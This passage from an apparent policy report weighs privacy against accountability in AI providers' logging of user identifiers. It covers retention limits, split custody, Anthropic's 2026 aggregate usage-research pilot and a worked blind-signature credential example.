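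Theft can expose metadata even when conversations are safe. In November 2025, OpenAI disclosed that an attacker had taken data from Mixpanel, a company that analysed use of OpenAI's API website. The data included account holders' names, email addresses, approximate locations and user IDs, but no prompts or answers. A criminal could use these details to write a convincing fake message from OpenAI to a developer whose API key gives access to a whole company's account.

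Neither case depended on the codes that deployers send for their end users. But each new field adds to the data that a court can demand or a thief can steal, and copying it to a gateway, a provider and several tool servers increases the number of places they can get it from.

### Zero retention and abuse monitoring

Hospitals, law firms and other customers with confidential data often want a zero-retention contract, under which the provider discards prompts and answers after replying. This is the best protection against exposure, since it leaves no record to steal or demand. The 2025 preservation order did not cover API customers with such contracts.

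It also removes the history a provider needs to recognise misuse spread over many requests. A filter can still examine each request as it passes through, but nobody can go back to an earlier request when a later one raises suspicion.

The provider could keep a short record without the text:

```json
{"user": "5a19f3b06c", "time": "2026-12-01T09:00Z", "category": "cyber"}
```

A monitor could tell from ten such records in a week that something deserves attention, but a reviewer couldn't tell from them whether the filter had been right. The bank's hired tester would have ten accusations on file and no text to answer them with. Discarding content therefore protects people's privacy but can make it harder for them to clear their names. A customer could reduce this problem by keeping the text for a limited time and producing it if the provider asks. That would work for an honest hospital, but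 not for a customer who is the source of the misuse.

### Keeping less and dividing it

A short retention period limits exposure while still allowing monitoring, but choosing the period is difficult. In 2025, OpenAI's standard limit for abuse-monitoring logs of API requests was 30 days. The authorities learned of the Medicare breach and the false murder tip only after more than 80 days, by which time a log with a 30-day limit would no longer have contained any record of them.

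A company could instead delete different data at different times. It might keep full text for 30 days and codes, times and trace IDs for six months. An investigator who arrived on day 81 could still find out which companies had handled a task, but not what the model had read. The company could keep flagged text for longer, but it would need a fixed deletion date so that text flagged by mistake wasn't kept indefinitely.

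Split custody keeps the data but divides it between people. The EDPB describes a company whose app gives medical advice. Its quality-control team checks the advice but sees only codes in place of patients' names. If it finds that a patient got bad advice, it sends the code and a message to a second team, which holds the names and contacts the patient. In a more elaborate example, a separate trust centre holds the means of matching codes across hospitals and research groups, and a board must approve each research project.

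AI services already have part of this arrangement when the deployer keeps the names and sends the provider random codes. A firm could extend it to its own logs by giving investigators the traces and leaving the table of names with another department, such as legal. This would stop curious staff from browsing a colleague's questions. But the arrangement slows investigators down during an attack, and it fails if the two sides collude or a court orders both to hand over their records. It also hides little if the prompts contain names.

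### Aggregate results and Anthropic's pilot

Some questions about AI use can be answered without anyone seeing an individual record. In 2026, Anthropic let three outside groups study how people use Claude without giving them access to any conversations. The groups were a Stanford laboratory, an Oxford laboratory and METR, a non-profit that evaluates advanced AI models (Anthropic, *Enabling independent research on how people use Claude*, 2026). Anthropic believes these were the first public studies of an AI company's own usage data by independent outsiders.

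Each research group wrote questions, such as what task a user was working on. Claude then answered them for about 250,000 conversations from April and May 2026. Anthropic's software clustered similar answers, dropped any cluster with too few conversations or accounts, and produced descriptions and counts. Anthropic's *Appendix to “Enabling independent research on how people use Claude”* (2026) explains that staff also reviewed every cluster of open-ended answers before releasing it. Excluding one Oxford question, they removed or redacted 1.8% to 3.3% of these clusters in each study. They withdrew all results for that question because its wording had probably produced misleading answers.

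To test the privacy protections, Anthropic gave the results to specialists at Imperial College London, who had two weeks and $1,000 in Claude credits to try to re-identify users. They identified no one, but they did connect one group of conversations to a popular open-source project because the description repeated distinctive wording from the tool. Anthropic plans to raise the minimum group sizes substantially.

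Readers can also use subtraction to recover small numbers that the software suppressed. If the results for a group of 100 conversations show low frustration in 70% and medium frustration in 29%, the remaining conversation must have had high frustration. Anthropic doesn't count this as a harm unless it reveals something about an identifiable person or organisation.

In the pilot, the Stanford group found that people delegated consequential work, meaning work that affects others or is hard to undo, in more than half of the conversations. This work often involved legal and financial questions. The result shows how much a leak of individual conversations could reveal.

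The method has two serious weaknesses for oversight. Nobody could read the underlying conversations, so mistakes in Claude's answers were hard to catch. Some questions that had worked when researchers tested them on a public set of chats also gave misleading results on real Claude traffic. For example, a question that makes Claude name a problem in every conversation will lead it to report problems where there are none.

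The outsiders also depended on the company they were studying. Anthropic's contracts allowed them to publish unwelcome findings, but its staff made the final decision about which data to release. The staff shared most of the results about misuse but withheld descriptions of how users had bypassed safeguards.

Aggregate results can show how common a practice is but are almost useless for finding one offender. The employee's request would not have appeared, because the pilot excluded API customers. Even if the sample had included it, one stolen contract would have fallen below the minimum group size. The studies also could not follow a user over several months, because each drew its own random sample from a fixed window. Anthropic says it would reconsider the risks before supporting research that tracks use over time.

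### Proving a fact without giving a name

A provider that offers special help to security testers needs to know that someone is an authorised tester, but may not need to know which one. An anonymous credential lets a person prove such a fact without revealing their identity. One of the simplest kinds uses a blind signature, which the cryptographer David Chaum proposed in the early 1980s. The IETF's Privacy Pass standards, published in 2024, include a version that lets people prove to websites that they have passed a check.

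Suppose an issuer, such as a professional body, verifies the bank's tester. To show the arithmetic, the following steps use small numbers and keep only the remainder after dividing each result by 33.

1. The issuer publishes a key consisting of 33 and 3, which it reserves for authorised testers. It keeps a matching secret number, 7.
2. The tester's app creates a random token and computes its hash, which in this example is 5. It also picks a secret blinding number, 2. It calculates 5 × 2³ = 40, which leaves a remainder of 7, and sends this 7 to the issuer.
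3. The issuer, which knows the tester's name but not the token, signs by raising 7 to its secret power. 7⁷ leaves a remainder of 28, and the issuer returns 28.
4. The app divides 28 by its blinding number and gets 14. This is exactly the signature that the issuer would have produced if it had signed 5 directly.
5. The app later sends the token and the signature, 14, to the AI provider along with a request.
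6. The provider hashes the token and gets 5. It then calculates 14³ = 2,744, which also leaves a remainder of 5, so the signature is valid. It adds the token to a list of spent tokens so that nobody can use it again.

In general, for a hash *h*, blinding number *r*, public exponent *e*, secret exponent *d* and modulus *N*, the app obtains

(*h* · *r*ᵉ)ᵈ / *r* = *h*ᵈ (mod *N*)

Real keys have more than 600 digits, so an attacker can't work out the secret exponent. The issuer saw 7 and 28, and the provider saw 5 and 14. For every tester the issuer has approved, some blinding number would connect that tester's values to this token, so the two companies can't identify the tester even if they combine their records.

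This protection has practical limits. If the issuer has approved only three testers, the token narrows the search to three people. A dishonest issuer could use a separate key for one tester and recognise the tokens signed with it, so apps need a way to check that the issuer uses the same key for everyone. The request also still comes with a network address, a deployer's account and perhaps a `safety_identifier`, any of which could identify the tester.

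The same protection also shields testers who abuse their tokens. If an approved tester used a token to attack a hospital, the provider could refuse the request, but it couldn't recognise the tester's next token. The issuer couldn't say whose token it was, even under a court order. The issuer could limit the damage by giving each tester only 20 tokens a day, but a tester could sell those 20 to a criminal without either company finding out who had sold them. As a last resort, the issuer could retire the key, but that would cut off every honest tester too.

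More complex credentials can restore some control. One type gives each holder a stable code at each provider, which the holder can't change and the issuer can't trace. If the provider bans a code, the person can't return under a new one, but the provider can also link all of that person's requests. Another type includes the holder's encrypted name, which a trustee can unlock to trace the holder after serious abuse. However, a government can compel the trustee, or a thief can attack it. Designers can choose how much anonymity to give up, but they can't make a credential traceable only for abusers, because it has to work before anyone knows who the abusers are.

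### Two cases that are hard to answer

Privacy advocates can point out that the people who lose privacy because of these fields are not the people who benefit from them. Every honest user gets a longer, more easily searched record, while a determined criminal can avoid leaving a useful one by using a stolen account, inventing a new code for each request or running an open model at home. People may also stop asking an AI system about an abortion, a debt or a violent partner if they think the question will stay linked to them. A company's promises about how it will use the data offer limited reassurance, because it can change its policy, suffer a breach or receive a court order. In FTC cases, companies treated a meaningless-looking code as permission to share data, and the agency replied that "the opacity of an identifier cannot be an excuse for improper use or disclosure".

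Accountability advocates can answer that withholding metadata doesn't stop surveillance by the companies that already have the prompts. Without a retention limit or a zero-retention contract, a provider can read what the employee typed whether or not a code accompanies it. Leaving out the code mainly hinders investigators. It can also hurt honest users, since a provider that can't tell a reseller's customers apart may block them all. Outsiders such as the supplier and the Philadelphia police never agreed to any of this, and they can't protect themselves with a privacy setting. Anthropic argues that understanding AI's effects on society is too big a job for AI companies alone.

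The privacy argument is strongest against identifiers that work across companies, and against flags and personal details sent with them, because these create user histories that no single company has today. It is much weaker against a random code that one provider can use and only the deployer can trace. The accountability argument is stronger for such a code than for cross-company identifiers, because most of its examples require telling users apart within a service and few require the provider to know a name. The two sides therefore disagree less about whether to send a code than about how long it should last and who may ask the deployer for the name behind it.
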